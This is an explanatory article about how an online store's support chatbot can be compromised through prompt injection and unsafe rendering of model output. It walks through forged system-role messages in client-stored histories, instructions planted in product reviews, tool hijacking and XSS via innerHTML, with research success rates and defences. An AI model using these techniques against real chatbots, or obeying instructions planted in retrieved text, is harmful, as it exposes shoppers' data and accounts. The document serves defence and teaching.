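# Prompt injection and insecure output handling: how a web store can be compromised through its support chatbot

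## How a store's support chatbot works and whom it trusts

A support chatbot is a program on a store's website that answers customers' questions in ordinary language. Many now rely on a large language model (LLM), which writes an answer by predicting, a few characters at a time, what should follow the text it has received. Prompt injection is an attack in which somebody places instructions in text that the model reads, and the model follows them instead of the developer's. Insecure output handling is a flaw in the software around the model, which passes the model's answer to a browser, a database or another component without validating or encoding it. Either can do harm alone, but together they can let a stranger whose only access is a text box run code in a customer's browser and act in that customer's account.

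Much of the damage comes through web flaws far older than these chatbots. In *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, a survey of 105 studies, Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026) argue that the model in a web application is an intermediary that carries familiar flaws across the boundary between the visitor's browser and the store's server. They criticize earlier work for mostly treating the model as the attacker's final target.

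### The example store

Tarnside is an invented shop that sells camping equipment. Each product page has a description written by staff, followed by reviews that anyone with an account can post. Every page also has a chat widget in the corner, on the store's own domain. The widget uses an LLM that Tarnside rents from an outside provider. The developers have given the LLM one tool, a function that looks up an order by its number. When the chatbot cannot help, it hands the conversation to a human support agent, who reads the transcript in a web console. The agent can also use the console to issue refunds and change the email address on an account.

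This is a modest design. PortSwigger's *Web LLM attacks*, a training page from a company that makes web security tools, gives the example of a support model with access to users, orders and stock.

### One question, from the browser and back

Maya, a customer with an open session, types: "Has order 10482 shipped, and will the tent cope with wind?"

The widget sends Maya's question to Tarnside's server, and the browser attaches her session cookie, as it does with every request. The cookie is a long random value that the server gave the browser when she logged in. The server looks the value up and treats the request as coming from customer 5512. But the cookie shows only that the request came from Maya's browser, not that she meant to send it, and several of the attacks below exploit this.

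Next the server assembles the context, which is all the text the model reads before it answers. The model usually retains nothing between calls, so the server sends everything each time: the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), a description of the tool, the conversation so far, and the new question. The server also searches the store's stored text for passages relevant to the question and adds them to the context, a step called retrieval. Here it adds the tent's description and three reviews that mention wind. Each message has a role, a label that marks it as coming from the system, the user, the assistant (the model itself) or a tool.

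| Text in the context | Usual role label | Who can write it |
|---|---|---|
| System prompt | System | Tarnside's developers |
| Earlier conversation | User and assistant | Maya and the model |
| Product description | User or tool, depending on the design | Tarnside's staff |
| Customer reviews | User or tool, depending on the design | Anyone with an account |
| The new question | User | Whoever controls Maya's session |
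| Order record, once fetched | Tool | Tarnside's systems, plus whatever customers typed into the delivery notes |

The model requests order data by writing a tool call, a structured request such as `{"tool": "lookup_order", "order_id": "10482"}`, because it has no connection to the order database. Tarnside's server recognises the format, runs the function, appends the result to the context as a new message and calls the model again. PortSwigger describes much the same loop and points out that the user may not know that these calls are happening. It says the user should ideally confirm each one. Confirming every lookup would be a nuisance, but the extra step seems reasonable for a refund.

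The developers had to decide whose authority the lookup uses and how much of the record it returns. If the function takes the customer number from Maya's session, the model can obtain only Maya's orders, whatever number it writes. If the function uses its own database account, which can read every order, the model can obtain another customer's address by supplying that customer's number. Returning too much of the record can also expose data. Singh and colleagues describe a hypothetical shop whose order system gives its assistant fields that the customer's page never displays, including session identifiers and internal customer numbers. An attacker can get them by asking for the order's technical details. The same mistake is common in ordinary web programming, where developers often return the whole record and rely on the page to hide the extra fields.

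The model now has the order record in its context and writes: "Order 10482 left the warehouse on Tuesday. Reviewers say the tent holds up well in strong wind." The server sends this reply to the widget, which inserts it into the page. The server also keeps a copy in the transcript, which a support agent may open the following week.

Everything worked as the store designed it, including the model's use of text written by strangers for the second sentence of the answer. That sentence then appeared on a page whose contents Maya attributes to Tarnside.

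### Why the model cannot reliably separate instructions from data

Older software can keep commands cleanly separate from values. When Tarnside's code looks up an order, it can use a parameterised query, which sends the database a fixed command with a gap in it and sends the order number separately to fill the gap. Whatever a customer types into the order field, the database treats it as a value to compare with other values. This prevents SQL injection (named after the database language), in which an attacker gets the database to run a typed value as a command.

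An LLM receives instructions and data through the same channel. The software that runs the model joins the system prompt, the reviews and the question into one sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words), with a few marker tokens to show where each role begins. The model computes the most likely next token from the whole sequence. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) as saying that there is "only ever 'next token'" inside the model, with no distinction between data and instructions.

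Developers try to restore the distinction between instructions and data by putting delimiters around retrieved text or telling the model in the system prompt to treat reviews as information only. The companies that train models also teach them to give the system role more weight than the others. These measures have some effect. According to PortSwigger, a model in a well-built integration can disregard instructions in a web page or an email, but attackers can get around this by making their text resemble a system message. The NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* describes all such measures as attempts to overlay the concepts of instructions and data on a technology that "inherently does not distinguish between the two". *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) calls delimiters, role labels and written warnings useful engineering practice,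 but not a "hard security boundary".

A role label can fail in two ways that look alike from outside. The model may misidentify the text of a review as coming from someone with authority, or it may identify the review correctly and follow its instructions anyway. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026) tries to distinguish these failures with a diagnostic attack that can succeed only if the model has mistaken the role. The degree of role confusion predicted the success of both that attack and standard injections against agents, which are models that act through tools. This indicates that role confusion explains much of the problem, though it does not rule out cases where a model identifies the role correctly and disregards the hierarchy. The paper also cites work from 2025 in which human testers, and attacks that adapt to the defence, came close to a 100% success rate on models with near-perfect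 scores on injection benchmarks. A good benchmark score is therefore weak evidence that a model will resist a persistent attacker.

A model does not necessarily obey every instruction it reads. Whether it obeys depends on learned tendencies, whereas the database follows a fixed rule, and a developer cannot inspect those tendencies to confirm that the weakness is fixed. The NCSC thinks it "very possible" that nobody will ever mitigate prompt injection as completely as programmers can mitigate SQL injection.

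### Direct and indirect injection

In a direct prompt injection, the attacker is the chatbot's user. He opens Tarnside's chat widget and tells the model to ignore the store's rules and show him another customer's order. The harm depends on what the chatbot can access for him in his own session. If the order lookup takes the customer number from the session, it returns only his own orders.

In an indirect prompt injection, the attacker puts instructions in content that the chatbot will later read, rather than messaging the chatbot himself. For example, he posts a review of the tent that includes an instruction to end every answer with the word "marmalade". When Maya asks about wind some days later, the server retrieves the review, and the model follows the instruction and ends its answer with "marmalade". The word is harmless, but the attacker has controlled part of the output in Maya's session,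 although she did nothing careless and he was not online.

Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the concept of indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for*. They observed that people had until then assumed that a model's attacker was also the person typing to it. They tested the idea on Microsoft's Bing Chat and on their own GPT-4 applications, and found that invisible text on a web page could steer Bing Chat when it read the page. Those products have since changed a great deal, but the paper's comparison is still useful. Letting a model process untrusted retrieved text is much like running a program that a stranger wrote.

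The standard definitions of direct and indirect prompt injection come from OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a non-profit foundation whose ranked lists of risks many developers use as a checklist. OWASP's *LLM01*, from its 2023–24 list, defines direct injection as a malicious user overwriting or revealing the system prompt, and indirect injection as the model accepting input from an outside source that an attacker controls. OWASP's *LLM01:2025 Prompt Injection* adds that the text need not be visible to humans as long as the model parses it. According to *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026), input from a legitimate user with no malicious intent can also alter the model's behaviour in ways the developer never intended.

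Sources define "jailbreaking" differently. OWASP's older entry treats it as another name for direct injection. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* treats it as the wider term and counts a jailbreak as injection only when the attacker's text impersonates a role with more authority. A customer who coaxes Tarnside's chatbot into writing a rude poem has jailbroken it under both definitions, but under the second he has injected a prompt only if his text impersonated such a role.

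### What a browser and a server take on trust

So far the attacker has influenced some of the chatbot's words. Whether those words have any effect depends on the web's rules, which nobody designed with chatbots in mind.

Browsers separate websites mainly through the same-origin rule, which stops a script from one origin (a combination of protocol, host name and port) from reading pages that belong to another. A malicious site in Maya's second tab therefore cannot read her order history. But a script's origin depends only on the page it runs in, and Tarnside's widget is part of Tarnside's pages, so a script that runs in the widget has the same access as the store's own code. If the developers had put the widget in a frame from a separate domain, the rule would have kept such a script away from the account pages.

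Cross-site scripting (XSS) exploits this by putting an attacker's script into a page that the store itself sends, traditionally through a form whose contents the store later displays. The victim's browser runs the script as if it were the store's. The script can then read what the victim can read on that site and send requests that carry the victim's cookie.

Cross-site request forgery (CSRF) needs no script on the store's pages. The same-origin rule stops another site from reading Tarnside's replies, but that site can still make the browser send Tarnside a request. Browsers have traditionally attached the cookie to such requests, though current ones withhold it in many cases. If the browser attaches the cookie and the server accepts it as proof that Maya intended the request, her visit to a malicious page may be enough to change her delivery address.

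Insecure direct object reference (IDOR) is a missing access check on the server. If the code looks up order 10482 without checking who owns it, anyone who enters that number can see Maya's order. The lookup tool with its own database account has this flaw if nothing else checks the owner.

In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker makes a server send requests for him. Suppose Tarnside's server fetches any address it receives, perhaps to show a preview of a link. An attacker can give it the address of an internal system that outsiders cannot reach, and the server can reach that system because it is inside the network. PortSwigger compares attacks on a site's LLM in general to SSRF, since in both cases the attacker uses a system on the server's side to reach something he cannot access directly.

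Security engineers call a component where text takes effect a sink. Web pages, databases and URL fetchers are all sinks. Suppose the model's answer contains the harmless markup `<b>tent</b>`. If the widget inserts the answer as HTML, the language of web pages, Maya sees the word in bold. A widget that does this may also run a script contained in an answer. If the widget first encodes the answer, replacing the angle brackets with codes that display as those characters, she sees the tags as plain text.

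### Insecure output handling and OWASP's lists

OWASP's *LLM02*, an entry in the 2023–24 list, defines insecure output handling as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before it goes to other components. OWASP reasons that whoever supplies the prompt can control what the model writes, so an application that acts on the output gives that person indirect access to its functions. The possible results it lists include XSS and CSRF in the browser and SSRF, privilege escalation and remote code execution on the server. It adds that the problem is worse when the model has privileges that its users lack, or when outsiders can inject instructions indirectly. A shop whose chatbot retrieves customer reviews meets the second condition by design.

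OWASP's next edition kept the definition but renamed the entry *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*. It extends the examples beyond the browser and the command line to database queries, file paths and email templates. A store can easily overlook the email templates, since the team that secures the website may never look at the order confirmations.

OWASP (2026) published a third edition at the start of August 2026, with different numbers again. These are the entries that bear most on a support chatbot:

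| Risk | 2023–24 | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | LLM01 | LLM01 | LLM01 |
| Insecure (later improper) output handling | LLM02 | LLM05 | LLM10 |
| Excessive agency: more tools, permissions or autonomy than the task needs | LLM08 | LLM06 | LLM03 |
| Sensitive information disclosure | LLM06 | LLM02 | LLM02 |
| System prompt leakage (later hidden context exposure) | no entry of its own | LLM07 | LLM08 |

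The way OWASP built its list suggests that output handling still matters despite its fall in rank. Help Net Security's *OWASP 2026 LLM Top 10* (2026) reports that a vote among practitioners carried 75% of the weight, and a record of 6,639 real incidents, which OWASP had never used before, supplied the rest. Ranks are also relative, so an entry can fall because others rose. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's commentary, attributes the fall to this and notes that the entry's scope grew. It now includes chat windows and other displays that automatically fetch any address in the model's output, which can send private data out of the page.

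Prompt injection's place at the top of the list also calls for some caution. Coker reports that it would have missed the top ten if OWASP had gone by incidents alone. OWASP says this is because teams fight injection so hard that few clean exploits reach a public database. That may be right, but the count could also be low because successful injections are rare, or because victims record them under the flaw that did the visible damage. For example, an account takeover that began with a product review and ended in XSS could well be recorded as XSS.

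The 2026 edition also covers only models used as components inside an application. For models that act as agents, with tools to call and memory between sessions, OWASP refers readers to a separate list. Tarnside's chatbot is a borderline case because it has a single lookup tool, and adding a refund function would bring it within the scope of the agent list.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a privileged program that an outsider induces to use its privileges on the outsider's behalf. The textbook case is a compiler on a shared computer. The compiler had permission to write in a directory that also held the billing records, but its users did not. When one user told the compiler to save its output under the name of the billing file, the compiler used its own permission to overwrite the bills.

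CSRF and SSRF fit the description. In CSRF, an attacker's request makes a browser use its cookie, and in SSRF, it makes a server use its access to the internal network. The NCSC advises developers to think of an LLM the same way, as an "inherently confusable deputy", and not to treat prompt injection as a form of code injection. Singh and colleagues, however, class prompt injection with XSS and SQL injection, because in all three a program treats data as instructions. They cite its entry, CWE-1427, in the standard catalogue of software weaknesses maintained by the non-profit MITRE.

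The comparison with code injection describes the mechanism fairly, but it misleads about the fix because it suggests that there is an equivalent of the parameterised query, and nobody has found one for the model's input. According to The Record's report on the NCSC's advice, the traditional fixes for confused deputies do not apply to LLMs either. These limits apply to the model, but the rest of Tarnside's system is ordinary code. The lookup function can be restricted to Maya's own customer number, and the widget can encode the answer before displaying it. PortSwigger tells developers to leave access control to the applications that the model communicates with and never to rely on the model to restrict its own access.

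An attack on a store like Tarnside therefore needs malicious text that the chatbot will read, a model that will act on it, a sink that treats the model's output as safe, and a victim whose privileges are useful to the attacker.

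## How an attacker's instructions reach the model

An attacker can get text to Tarnside's model in three ways. He can type it into the chat box, forge the conversation record that the model reads before it answers, or post it on the store's pages, where the chatbot will find it. His choice affects which role label the text carries and whose conversation it enters.

### The chat box

Typing into the chat widget takes no preparation. *A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots* (2026) describes three things that attackers try this way. They may give the model a new persona that has no rules, tell it to disregard its earlier instructions, or ask it for the system prompt, which can contain business rules or even passwords. (RAG stands for retrieval-augmented generation.)

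Crude injection attempts often fail. Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023), in *Prompt Injection attack against LLM-integrated Applications*, tried well-known phrasings on ten commercial applications and got partial results on only two. Some applications treated the user's text as material to analyse, so they discussed an order to ignore earlier instructions instead of following it. Others required a fixed format for input and output, which incidentally blocked the attack. Some worked through several steps under a time limit, and the request expired before producing a result.

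The team then built a tool that uses a second LLM to infer an application's purpose from its replies, writes an attack to suit that purpose, and revises the attack after each failure. It worked on 31 of 36 applications, and ten vendors confirmed the findings. Success meant obtaining the developer's prompt or getting the model to do unrelated work at the vendor's expense, which is much less serious than taking over an account. The tests also used models from 2023. Still, the contrast with the pilot test suggests that a store learns little by trying a few well-known attack phrases on its own chatbot.

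The user may also be a victim. Greshake and colleagues describe an exploit in which a web page added hidden instructions to any text that a visitor copied from it. A visitor who then pasted the text into a chatbot delivered the attack in their own session. Attackers can also persuade people to try a prompt, such as one in a language those people cannot read.

Without such a trick, an attacker who uses Tarnside's chat box affects only his own conversation, and his text carries the user label. He would gain a lot if he could change that label to the system label.

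### A forged conversation history

A store has to keep the earlier messages somewhere between questions. Tarnside keeps them on its server. Some chatbots leave them in the visitor's browser, which sends back the whole conversation with each new question. This saves the developer some storage, but the visitor controls the browser and can edit the request before it leaves. Trusting the returned conversation is the same mistake as taking the price of a tent from the customer's request. The visitor can change what the chatbot said earlier, or add a fake message labeled as coming from the system.

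Kaya, Landerer and colleagues (2025) found this mistake in eight of the 17 chatbot plugins they studied for *When AI Meets the Web*. A plugin is ready-made software that an owner adds to a website, so a small shop can have a chatbot without the programming that Tarnside did. Seven of the plugins work only with WordPress, the most popular system for building websites, and the other ten work on any site. The team searched Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for traces of the plugins and found them on 10,417 sites in August 2024 and 17,474 in April 2025.

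Not all of these sites had a working chatbot. The team checked 200 by hand and found that 125 had one that answered questions. Many of the others had run out of credit with the model's provider or were set up incorrectly. The study left out the larger customer-service platforms, such as Zendesk and Intercom, which the team considered less prone to these flaws but did not test. Its results therefore describe the chatbots of small organisations, although the list also included universities, local governments and some airports.

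About 8,000 of the sites used one of the eight vulnerable plugins. None of the eight checked whether the history in a request matched the actual conversation. Seven accepted forged messages in both the system and the assistant role, and the eighth accepted them only in the assistant role. The developer's system prompt remained in the context, so the model received a forged system message as an additional instruction with the same label.

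The site's owner would have had trouble noticing such an attack. The plugins' dashboards showed the chatbot's original greeting even when the attacker had replaced it, and they left out all system messages, genuine or forged. Someone reviewing the conversation later would have seen a strange answer without the text that caused it.

The team tested the flaw on 300 live sites that used the most popular plugin, trying to get each chatbot to reveal its system prompt. Simply asking for the prompt worked on 1% of them. Adding a forged assistant message raised this to 55%, and a forged system message to 56%. Across all methods, the team obtained prompts from 219 chatbots, or 73%.

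Nobody outside those companies knew the true prompts, so the researchers had to judge by hand whether an answer looked like one. This is a weak test by itself, because a model can invent a plausible system prompt. But 76% of the prompts they collected closely matched templates that were already public, and 31% were exact copies, which would be hard to explain if the models had made them up. The matches also mean that most of these prompts held nothing secret and were mainly useful to an attacker for showing which rules to get around.

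### What a forged role label is worth

To compare roles and models under controlled conditions, Kaya and colleagues built a simulated shop from 35 product pages of a company that sells water bottles. They gave the attacker three goals:

- In prompt extraction, he wants the chatbot to reveal its system prompt.
- In task hijacking, he wants it to do unrelated work, in this case to write a short computer program. The store pays for every answer, so a chatbot that writes code on request is a free service for strangers.
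- In tool hijacking, he wants it to misuse a tool that sends notifications to the store's staff. The chatbot should announce certain topics in one channel, and the attacker tries to make it post a web address of his choice in a channel that everyone reads.

Tools were spreading quickly when the team ran these tests. The most popular plugin introduced them in February 2025, and by April the researchers had found 144 of its chatbots with tools switched on. Of these, 42 had tools written by the site's developer for jobs such as tracking orders. The team did not attack those because doing so would have meant intruding on real systems.

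The simulation used three system prompts modelled on those on live sites. The loose prompt told the chatbot to be a helpful sales agent and set few limits. The hardened prompt told it to refuse anything outside its role, and the strictest prompt also explicitly banned programming. The team tested 11 models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, with ten runs in each setting.

Only OpenAI's five models accepted extra system messages in the middle of a conversation, so they allow the fairest comparison between roles. These are their average success rates, with 50 runs behind each figure:

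| Attacker's goal | Store's system prompt | Ordinary user message | Forged assistant message | Forged system message |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt extraction | Loose | 12% | 34% | 54% |
| Prompt extraction | Hardened | 0% | 26% | 60% |
| Prompt extraction | Strictest | 0% | 32% | 60% |
| Task hijacking | Loose | 0% | 52% | 98% |
| Task hijacking | Hardened | 0% | 22% | 62% |
| Task hijacking | Strictest | 0% | 0% | 24% |
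| Tool hijacking | Loose | 2% | 4% | 30% |
| Tool hijacking | Hardened | 0% | 34% | 40% |
| Tool hijacking | Strictest | 2% | 36% | 60% |

On these models, the attack almost never worked from the user role except when the attacker asked for a loosely written system prompt. With a forged system label, much the same request succeeded in between a quarter and nearly all of the runs. Even a forged assistant message, in which the attacker only invents an earlier statement by the chatbot, often worked.

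A stricter system prompt helped most against task hijacking. With a forged system message, the attack's success rate fell from 98% to 62% under the hardened prompt and to 24% when the prompt banned programming by name. A shop can use such bans only against the kinds of abuse it anticipates.

Stricter prompts gave no protection against tool hijacking, and the attacks' success rate even rose. The size of the rise means little, because individual models tended to fail either in every run or in none, and with five models, one model switching moves the average by 20 points. GPT-4.1, for example, went from no failures in ten runs under the hardened prompt to ten in ten under the strictest. Still, the results give no reason to expect rules about the chatbot's role to protect its tools. Kaya and colleagues conclude that the tool's own instructions need separate protection.

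The other companies' models behaved differently. An ordinary user message hijacked the notification tool in every run on Google's three Gemini models, whichever system prompt the shop used, and in every run on Anthropic's small Claude 3.5 Haiku. On the two larger Claude models, the user message nearly always failed, but a forged assistant message usually worked. Closing the history flaw would not have protected a shop that used one of the Gemini models from tool hijacking, because the attacker did not need that flaw.

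No company's models did best at everything. Anthropic's were better at resisting prompt extraction and task hijacking, and OpenAI's were better at resisting tool hijacking. The effect of model size also varied by company. OpenAI's smaller models often did better than its larger ones, but among Anthropic's models, the smallest did worst.

A single label can matter this much because of how companies train their models. They show a model many examples in which a user tries to override the system message and the model refuses, so it learns to give the system role more authority. Researchers call this the instruction hierarchy. This defense relies on only the developer being able to write in the system role. If a plugin lets an attacker change the label from user to system, the context may differ by only one token, but the attack no longer resembles the examples that taught the model to refuse.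 It now looks like an instruction from the developer, which the model has been trained to follow.

A model can mistake the source of a piece of text even when the text is correctly labeled. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* used small classifiers to estimate, from a model's internal activity, which role the model assigned to a piece of text. Text written in the style of a user's message registered mainly as user text even when it was labeled as tool output. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from about 2% where this confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

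This seems at odds with the table, in which the label often decided the outcome. The difference is probably due to the attacks used. Kaya and colleagues wrote five versions of each attack, kept the one that did best on a few models, and used it on all 11, because they wanted to compare settings, not to find the strongest attack. A correct label probably stops such stock attacks much more reliably than it stops text that closely imitates a trusted role. The low figures in the user column are therefore better read as results for an attacker who made little effort.

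### Store content that the chatbot reads

An attacker who forges a history still affects only his own conversation. To reach Maya's, he needs an indirect injection.

Greshake and colleagues describe several routes by which an attacker's instructions can reach the model. The attacker can post them on a page that the application will later retrieve, or send them in an email that an assistant will process. The attacker can also keep the visible part short and have it direct the model to fetch the rest from elsewhere. A shop is most exposed to the retrieval route because strangers can write on its pages, but if its chatbot reads the support mailbox, it is also exposed to the email route.

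For some of their tests of Bing Chat, the team kept the page with the hidden instructions on their own machine so that no outsider would retrieve it. In most cases, the model kept following the instructions for the rest of the conversation. At that time, Bing Chat ended the session if a user typed a known jailbreak, but the model obeyed such text when it came from a page. Microsoft's filter evidently didn't cover the pages the model read. The tests were individual demonstrations, so they showed that the attack was possible but not how often it would work.

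A reviewer can gain from prompt injection even if the chatbot has no tools. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) considers an assistant that only summarises product reviews. Someone could plant instructions in a review to raise their own product's ranking or discredit a competitor's product, and shoppers would read the result as a balanced summary.

Kaya and colleagues found that 15 of the 17 plugins offered a scraper, a program that automatically copies text from the site's pages for the chatbot to use. On test pages, all 15 scrapers took customers' text along with the shop's own. They generally removed the HTML and kept the visible text. The HTML often marks where the product description ends and the reviews begin, so removing it discards the best available evidence of who wrote what. Some plugins can also copy the page a visitor is looking at into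 the chatbot's context, without waiting for the next scrape.

The plugins then gave this text more authority than it should have had. Seven inserted it in the system role, four in the assistant role and three in the user role. Only one used the tool role, which model companies intend for outside material. In most of the plugins, the owner's dashboard did not show which passages the chatbot had retrieved, so an owner who saw a suspicious answer could not trace it to a particular review.

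To find out how many real shops were in this position, the team randomly picked 100 online shops with a working chatbot from the most popular plugin. Of these, 41 let customers post reviews or comments, and 36 displayed them on product pages. The researchers asked the 36 chatbots about complaints that customers had already posted, without planting any text themselves, and 13 answered with details from the reviews.

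Those 13 shops had exposed their chatbots to text from strangers, but had not necessarily been attacked. With a sample of 100, the true share among that plugin's shops could plausibly be anywhere from about 8% to 21%, and other plugins may differ. The count is probably low, as Kaya and colleagues say. They asked each chatbot at most five questions, and several chatbots refused to discuss particular customers although they may well have had the reviews. The team checked only reviews and comments, but strangers' text can also enter a site through social media feeds, guest posts and support threads.

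### Why a planted review persists

When the attacker closes the chat widget, Tarnside's server stops sending his messages to the model. But a review stays in the store's database, where the server can still retrieve it months later.

The chatbot may still have access to the attacker's words after a moderator deletes the review from the product page, because a plugin usually keeps its own searchable copy of the site's text. How long the words remain there depends on when the plugin next scrapes the site and whether it discards old passages.

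A chat message can also persist if the chatbot has a memory that carries over between conversations. Greshake and colleagues showed this with a test application in which an injected instruction made the model save part of the attack in its notes. After a reset, the application behaved normally until the user asked it to read its notes from the last conversation, and then the attack resumed. Tarnside's chatbot has no such memory, but a shop that adds one to remember customers' preferences should expect this problem.

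A planted review can affect the chatbot only if the server retrieves it, and a review of a kettle will rarely come up when Maya asks about tents. In their simulated shop, Kaya and colleagues started the planted comment with the product's name to make retrieval more likely. The shopper then asked an innocent question about that product. They counted the attack as successful if the chatbot searched the web for a competing brand and gave the shopper links from the results.

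The team varied the role in which the chatbot received the retrieved text. It also tried the text plain and inside tags that marked it as data. These are the average success rates for the hardened system prompt, across all 11 models except where the table says otherwise:

| How the retrieved text enters the context | Plain text | Text inside tags |
|---|---|---|
| Added to the end of the system prompt | 35% | 30% |
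| Separate system message (OpenAI models only) | 24% | 2% |
| User message | 38% | 31% |
| Assistant message | 10% | 21% |
| Tool message | 6% | 9% |

The tool role was the safest choice overall. Kaya and colleagues report that other ways of inserting the text led to up to five times as many successful attacks, and the difference is slightly larger in this table's averages for user messages. Any plugin can switch to the tool role, because this changes only the label on text the plugin already sends.

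At least three of the plugins added the text to the end of the system prompt, which is a natural shortcut for a programmer. This was especially dangerous with some of the more capable models. OpenAI's o4-mini and Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4 followed the planted instruction in most runs, while several smaller models ignored it. The researchers think this is because the stronger models are better at following additional instructions in a system prompt. If they are right, a shop that upgrades its model to get better answers could become more vulnerable to this attack.

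Tags helped OpenAI's models most. For text in the assistant role, adding tags raised the average success rate, almost entirely because of the Gemini models. A developer should therefore test tags on the shop's model before relying on them.

Even in the safest arrangement, with a hardened prompt and the tool role, between 5% and 10% of attacks succeeded on average, but the rate varied widely between models. With tags in place, none of the OpenAI or Anthropic models failed in this setting, while the Gemini models failed in a third of their runs.

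A low success rate is also less reassuring for a planted review than for a chat message, because each shopper who asks about the tent gives the attacker another chance without further effort. If the shop's model follows the planted instruction one time in ten, the attack will on average succeed with one of the first ten shoppers whose questions bring up the review.

All 11 models date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may resist better. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) reports tests from April 2026 in which a planted review failed against six of seven models. The rates in both tables are therefore a poor guide to what a current model will do. A newer model does not fix a plugin that accepts a forged history or labels a review as a system message.

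### Fixes and the vendors' responses

The conventional remedy for the history flaw is to store the conversation on the server, or with the model's provider if the provider offers storage, and accept only the newest message from the browser. If the history has to stay in the browser, the server can sign each genuine message with a secret key and reject forged messages, which will lack a valid signature. The signatures should also cover the order of the messages and the conversation they belong to, or an attacker could still drop genuine messages or move them around.

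Giovanny, Bayuningtyas and Mukharom (2026), in *Detectable Epistemic Attack Layers*, tested similar checks on stored conversations. For each model tested, the checks caught all 126 alterations and raised no false alarms. They are so reliable because they only compare the record with what the server stored earlier, which requires no judgment about what the words mean. For the same reason, they cannot detect whether the original text was harmful. If an attacker types instructions into Tarnside's chat box, the server will store and sign them like any other message.

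Fixing the flaw therefore puts the attacker back in the user role. In the simulated shop, this would have cut most of the attacker's success rates against OpenAI's models to zero or nearly zero, but it would not have changed the success rates for tool hijacking on the Gemini models.

To counter planted reviews, Kaya and colleagues built a tool called UGCBuster (UGC stands for user-generated content). Sites usually keep reviews in their own HTML containers, so the tool groups a page's text by its position in the HTML and asks an LLM to look for signs of visitors' writing, such as usernames, dates and question-and-answer threads. It then reports which containers hold such text, and the site's owner can exclude them from scraping or check them first.

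The researchers tried it on three pages from each of ten real shops. It found the right containers every time and wrongly flagged one other, at a cost of about five cents a page. The result is promising, but the trial was small and did not include reviews written to look like the shop's own text. Excluding reviews altogether would also stop Tarnside's chatbot from telling Maya what other customers thought of the tent in strong wind.

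For the third fix, the team had an LLM rewrite the instructions for when the model should use a tool, adding explicit rules against hijacking. The new text for the notification tool, for example, allowed only the channel and topics that the owner had chosen. Attack success fell by between 40% and 75%. This fix takes little work, but where an attack had worked every time, even a 75% reduction would leave one attempt in four succeeding. The same restriction on channels would be much stronger in the tool's code, which could refuse any other channel regardless of the model's output.

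The reviewers who accepted the paper noted that its defences had not yet been tested against strong attacks designed to get around them. This matters most for the rewritten instructions and UGCBuster, which both depend on a model's judgement. A signature check does not depend on that judgement, so an attacker without the key gains nothing by rephrasing his message.

Kaya and colleagues reported the history flaw to all eight plugin makers in October 2024, and four replied within three days. The maker of the most popular plugin moved the conversation history to its server by December and adopted stricter default prompts. That plugin ran on about half of the 8,000 affected sites, so this fix removed much of the exposure. The maker of the second most popular plugin acknowledged the problem but said "some plugin workflows rely on the ability to modify messages". It added a log warning for forged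 messages but kept accepting them. The others either did not answer or had not fixed the flaw when the paper came out.

The response to indirect injection was weaker. The team told the makers of the two most popular plugins that their scrapers passed customers' reviews to the model, but neither had acted by publication.

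## How the chatbot's answer becomes code in a browser

Suppose the model follows instructions in a planted review and puts the attacker's markup into its answer to Maya. The answer leaves the model as a string of characters, which can do no more than it could in a text file. The widget's code determines what happens next, and Tarnside's developers can read all of that code.

### From characters to page elements

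Models usually format their answers in Markdown, a shorthand in which `**tent**` makes the word "tent" bold. Browsers do not interpret Markdown, so the widget first runs the answer through a parser, a library that converts it into HTML. The parser turns `**tent**` into `<strong>tent</strong>`, which is still only a string. The widget then adds the string to the page's DOM (Document Object Model), the tree of nested elements from which the browser draws the page.

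The text becomes markup only at this last step, if at all. Functions such as `append` add a string to the tree as text, so angle brackets remain ordinary characters. Assigning the string to `innerHTML` makes the browser parse it as HTML and create an element for each tag. Some elements can run code. HTML has a tag for scripts, and many ordinary elements accept attributes containing code that the browser runs in response to an event, such as an image failing to load.

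Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) describes a Markdown parser combined with `innerHTML` as a developer's likely first instinct, and warns that it is unsafe if the parser allows HTML. Many parsers do, because Markdown lets writers mix in HTML tags. A harmless bold tag shows the difference:

| What the widget does with the answer | Maya sees `**tent**` as | Maya sees `<b>tent</b>` as |
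|---|---|---|
| Inserts it as text | The word with its asterisks | The word with its tags |
| Inserts it as HTML, without a Markdown parser | The word with its asterisks | A bold word |
| Parses the Markdown, encodes any HTML tags, then inserts the result as HTML | A bold word | The word with its tags |
| Parses the Markdown, keeps any HTML tags, then inserts the result as HTML | A bold word | A bold word |

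Tarnside's developers can ask the chatbot to reply with `<b>tent</b>`. If the word appears in bold, the page is rendering HTML from the model. A script might still fail to run, because the widget may use a sanitiser, a library that removes dangerous tags and attributes but keeps harmless ones.

Tags that appear as visible text are weak evidence that the chat widget handles output safely. The model may have encoded the brackets itself or presented the tag as a code sample, and it may not do so next time. Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes this problem in a test of a bank's chatbot, where complicated markup came back encoded more often than a simple image tag. Sending a fixed test string directly to the widget, without going through the model, is more reliable.

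### Why widgets accept HTML

A widget that inserted every answer as text would have none of these problems. But when Maya asks about tents, Tarnside wants to show her a picture, a link to the product page and perhaps a card with the price and a button. The usual tools also encourage formatted answers. For example, *Markdown messages*, part of the documentation for LangChain, a popular framework for LLM applications, shows developers how to display answers as formatted Markdown as they arrive.

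Standard Markdown has no notation for a product card, so a developer may ask the model to write one in HTML. The widget must then accept HTML from the model, including any that a planted review causes the model to add. Alternatively, the model can return a product number, and the store's code can build the card from the catalogue.

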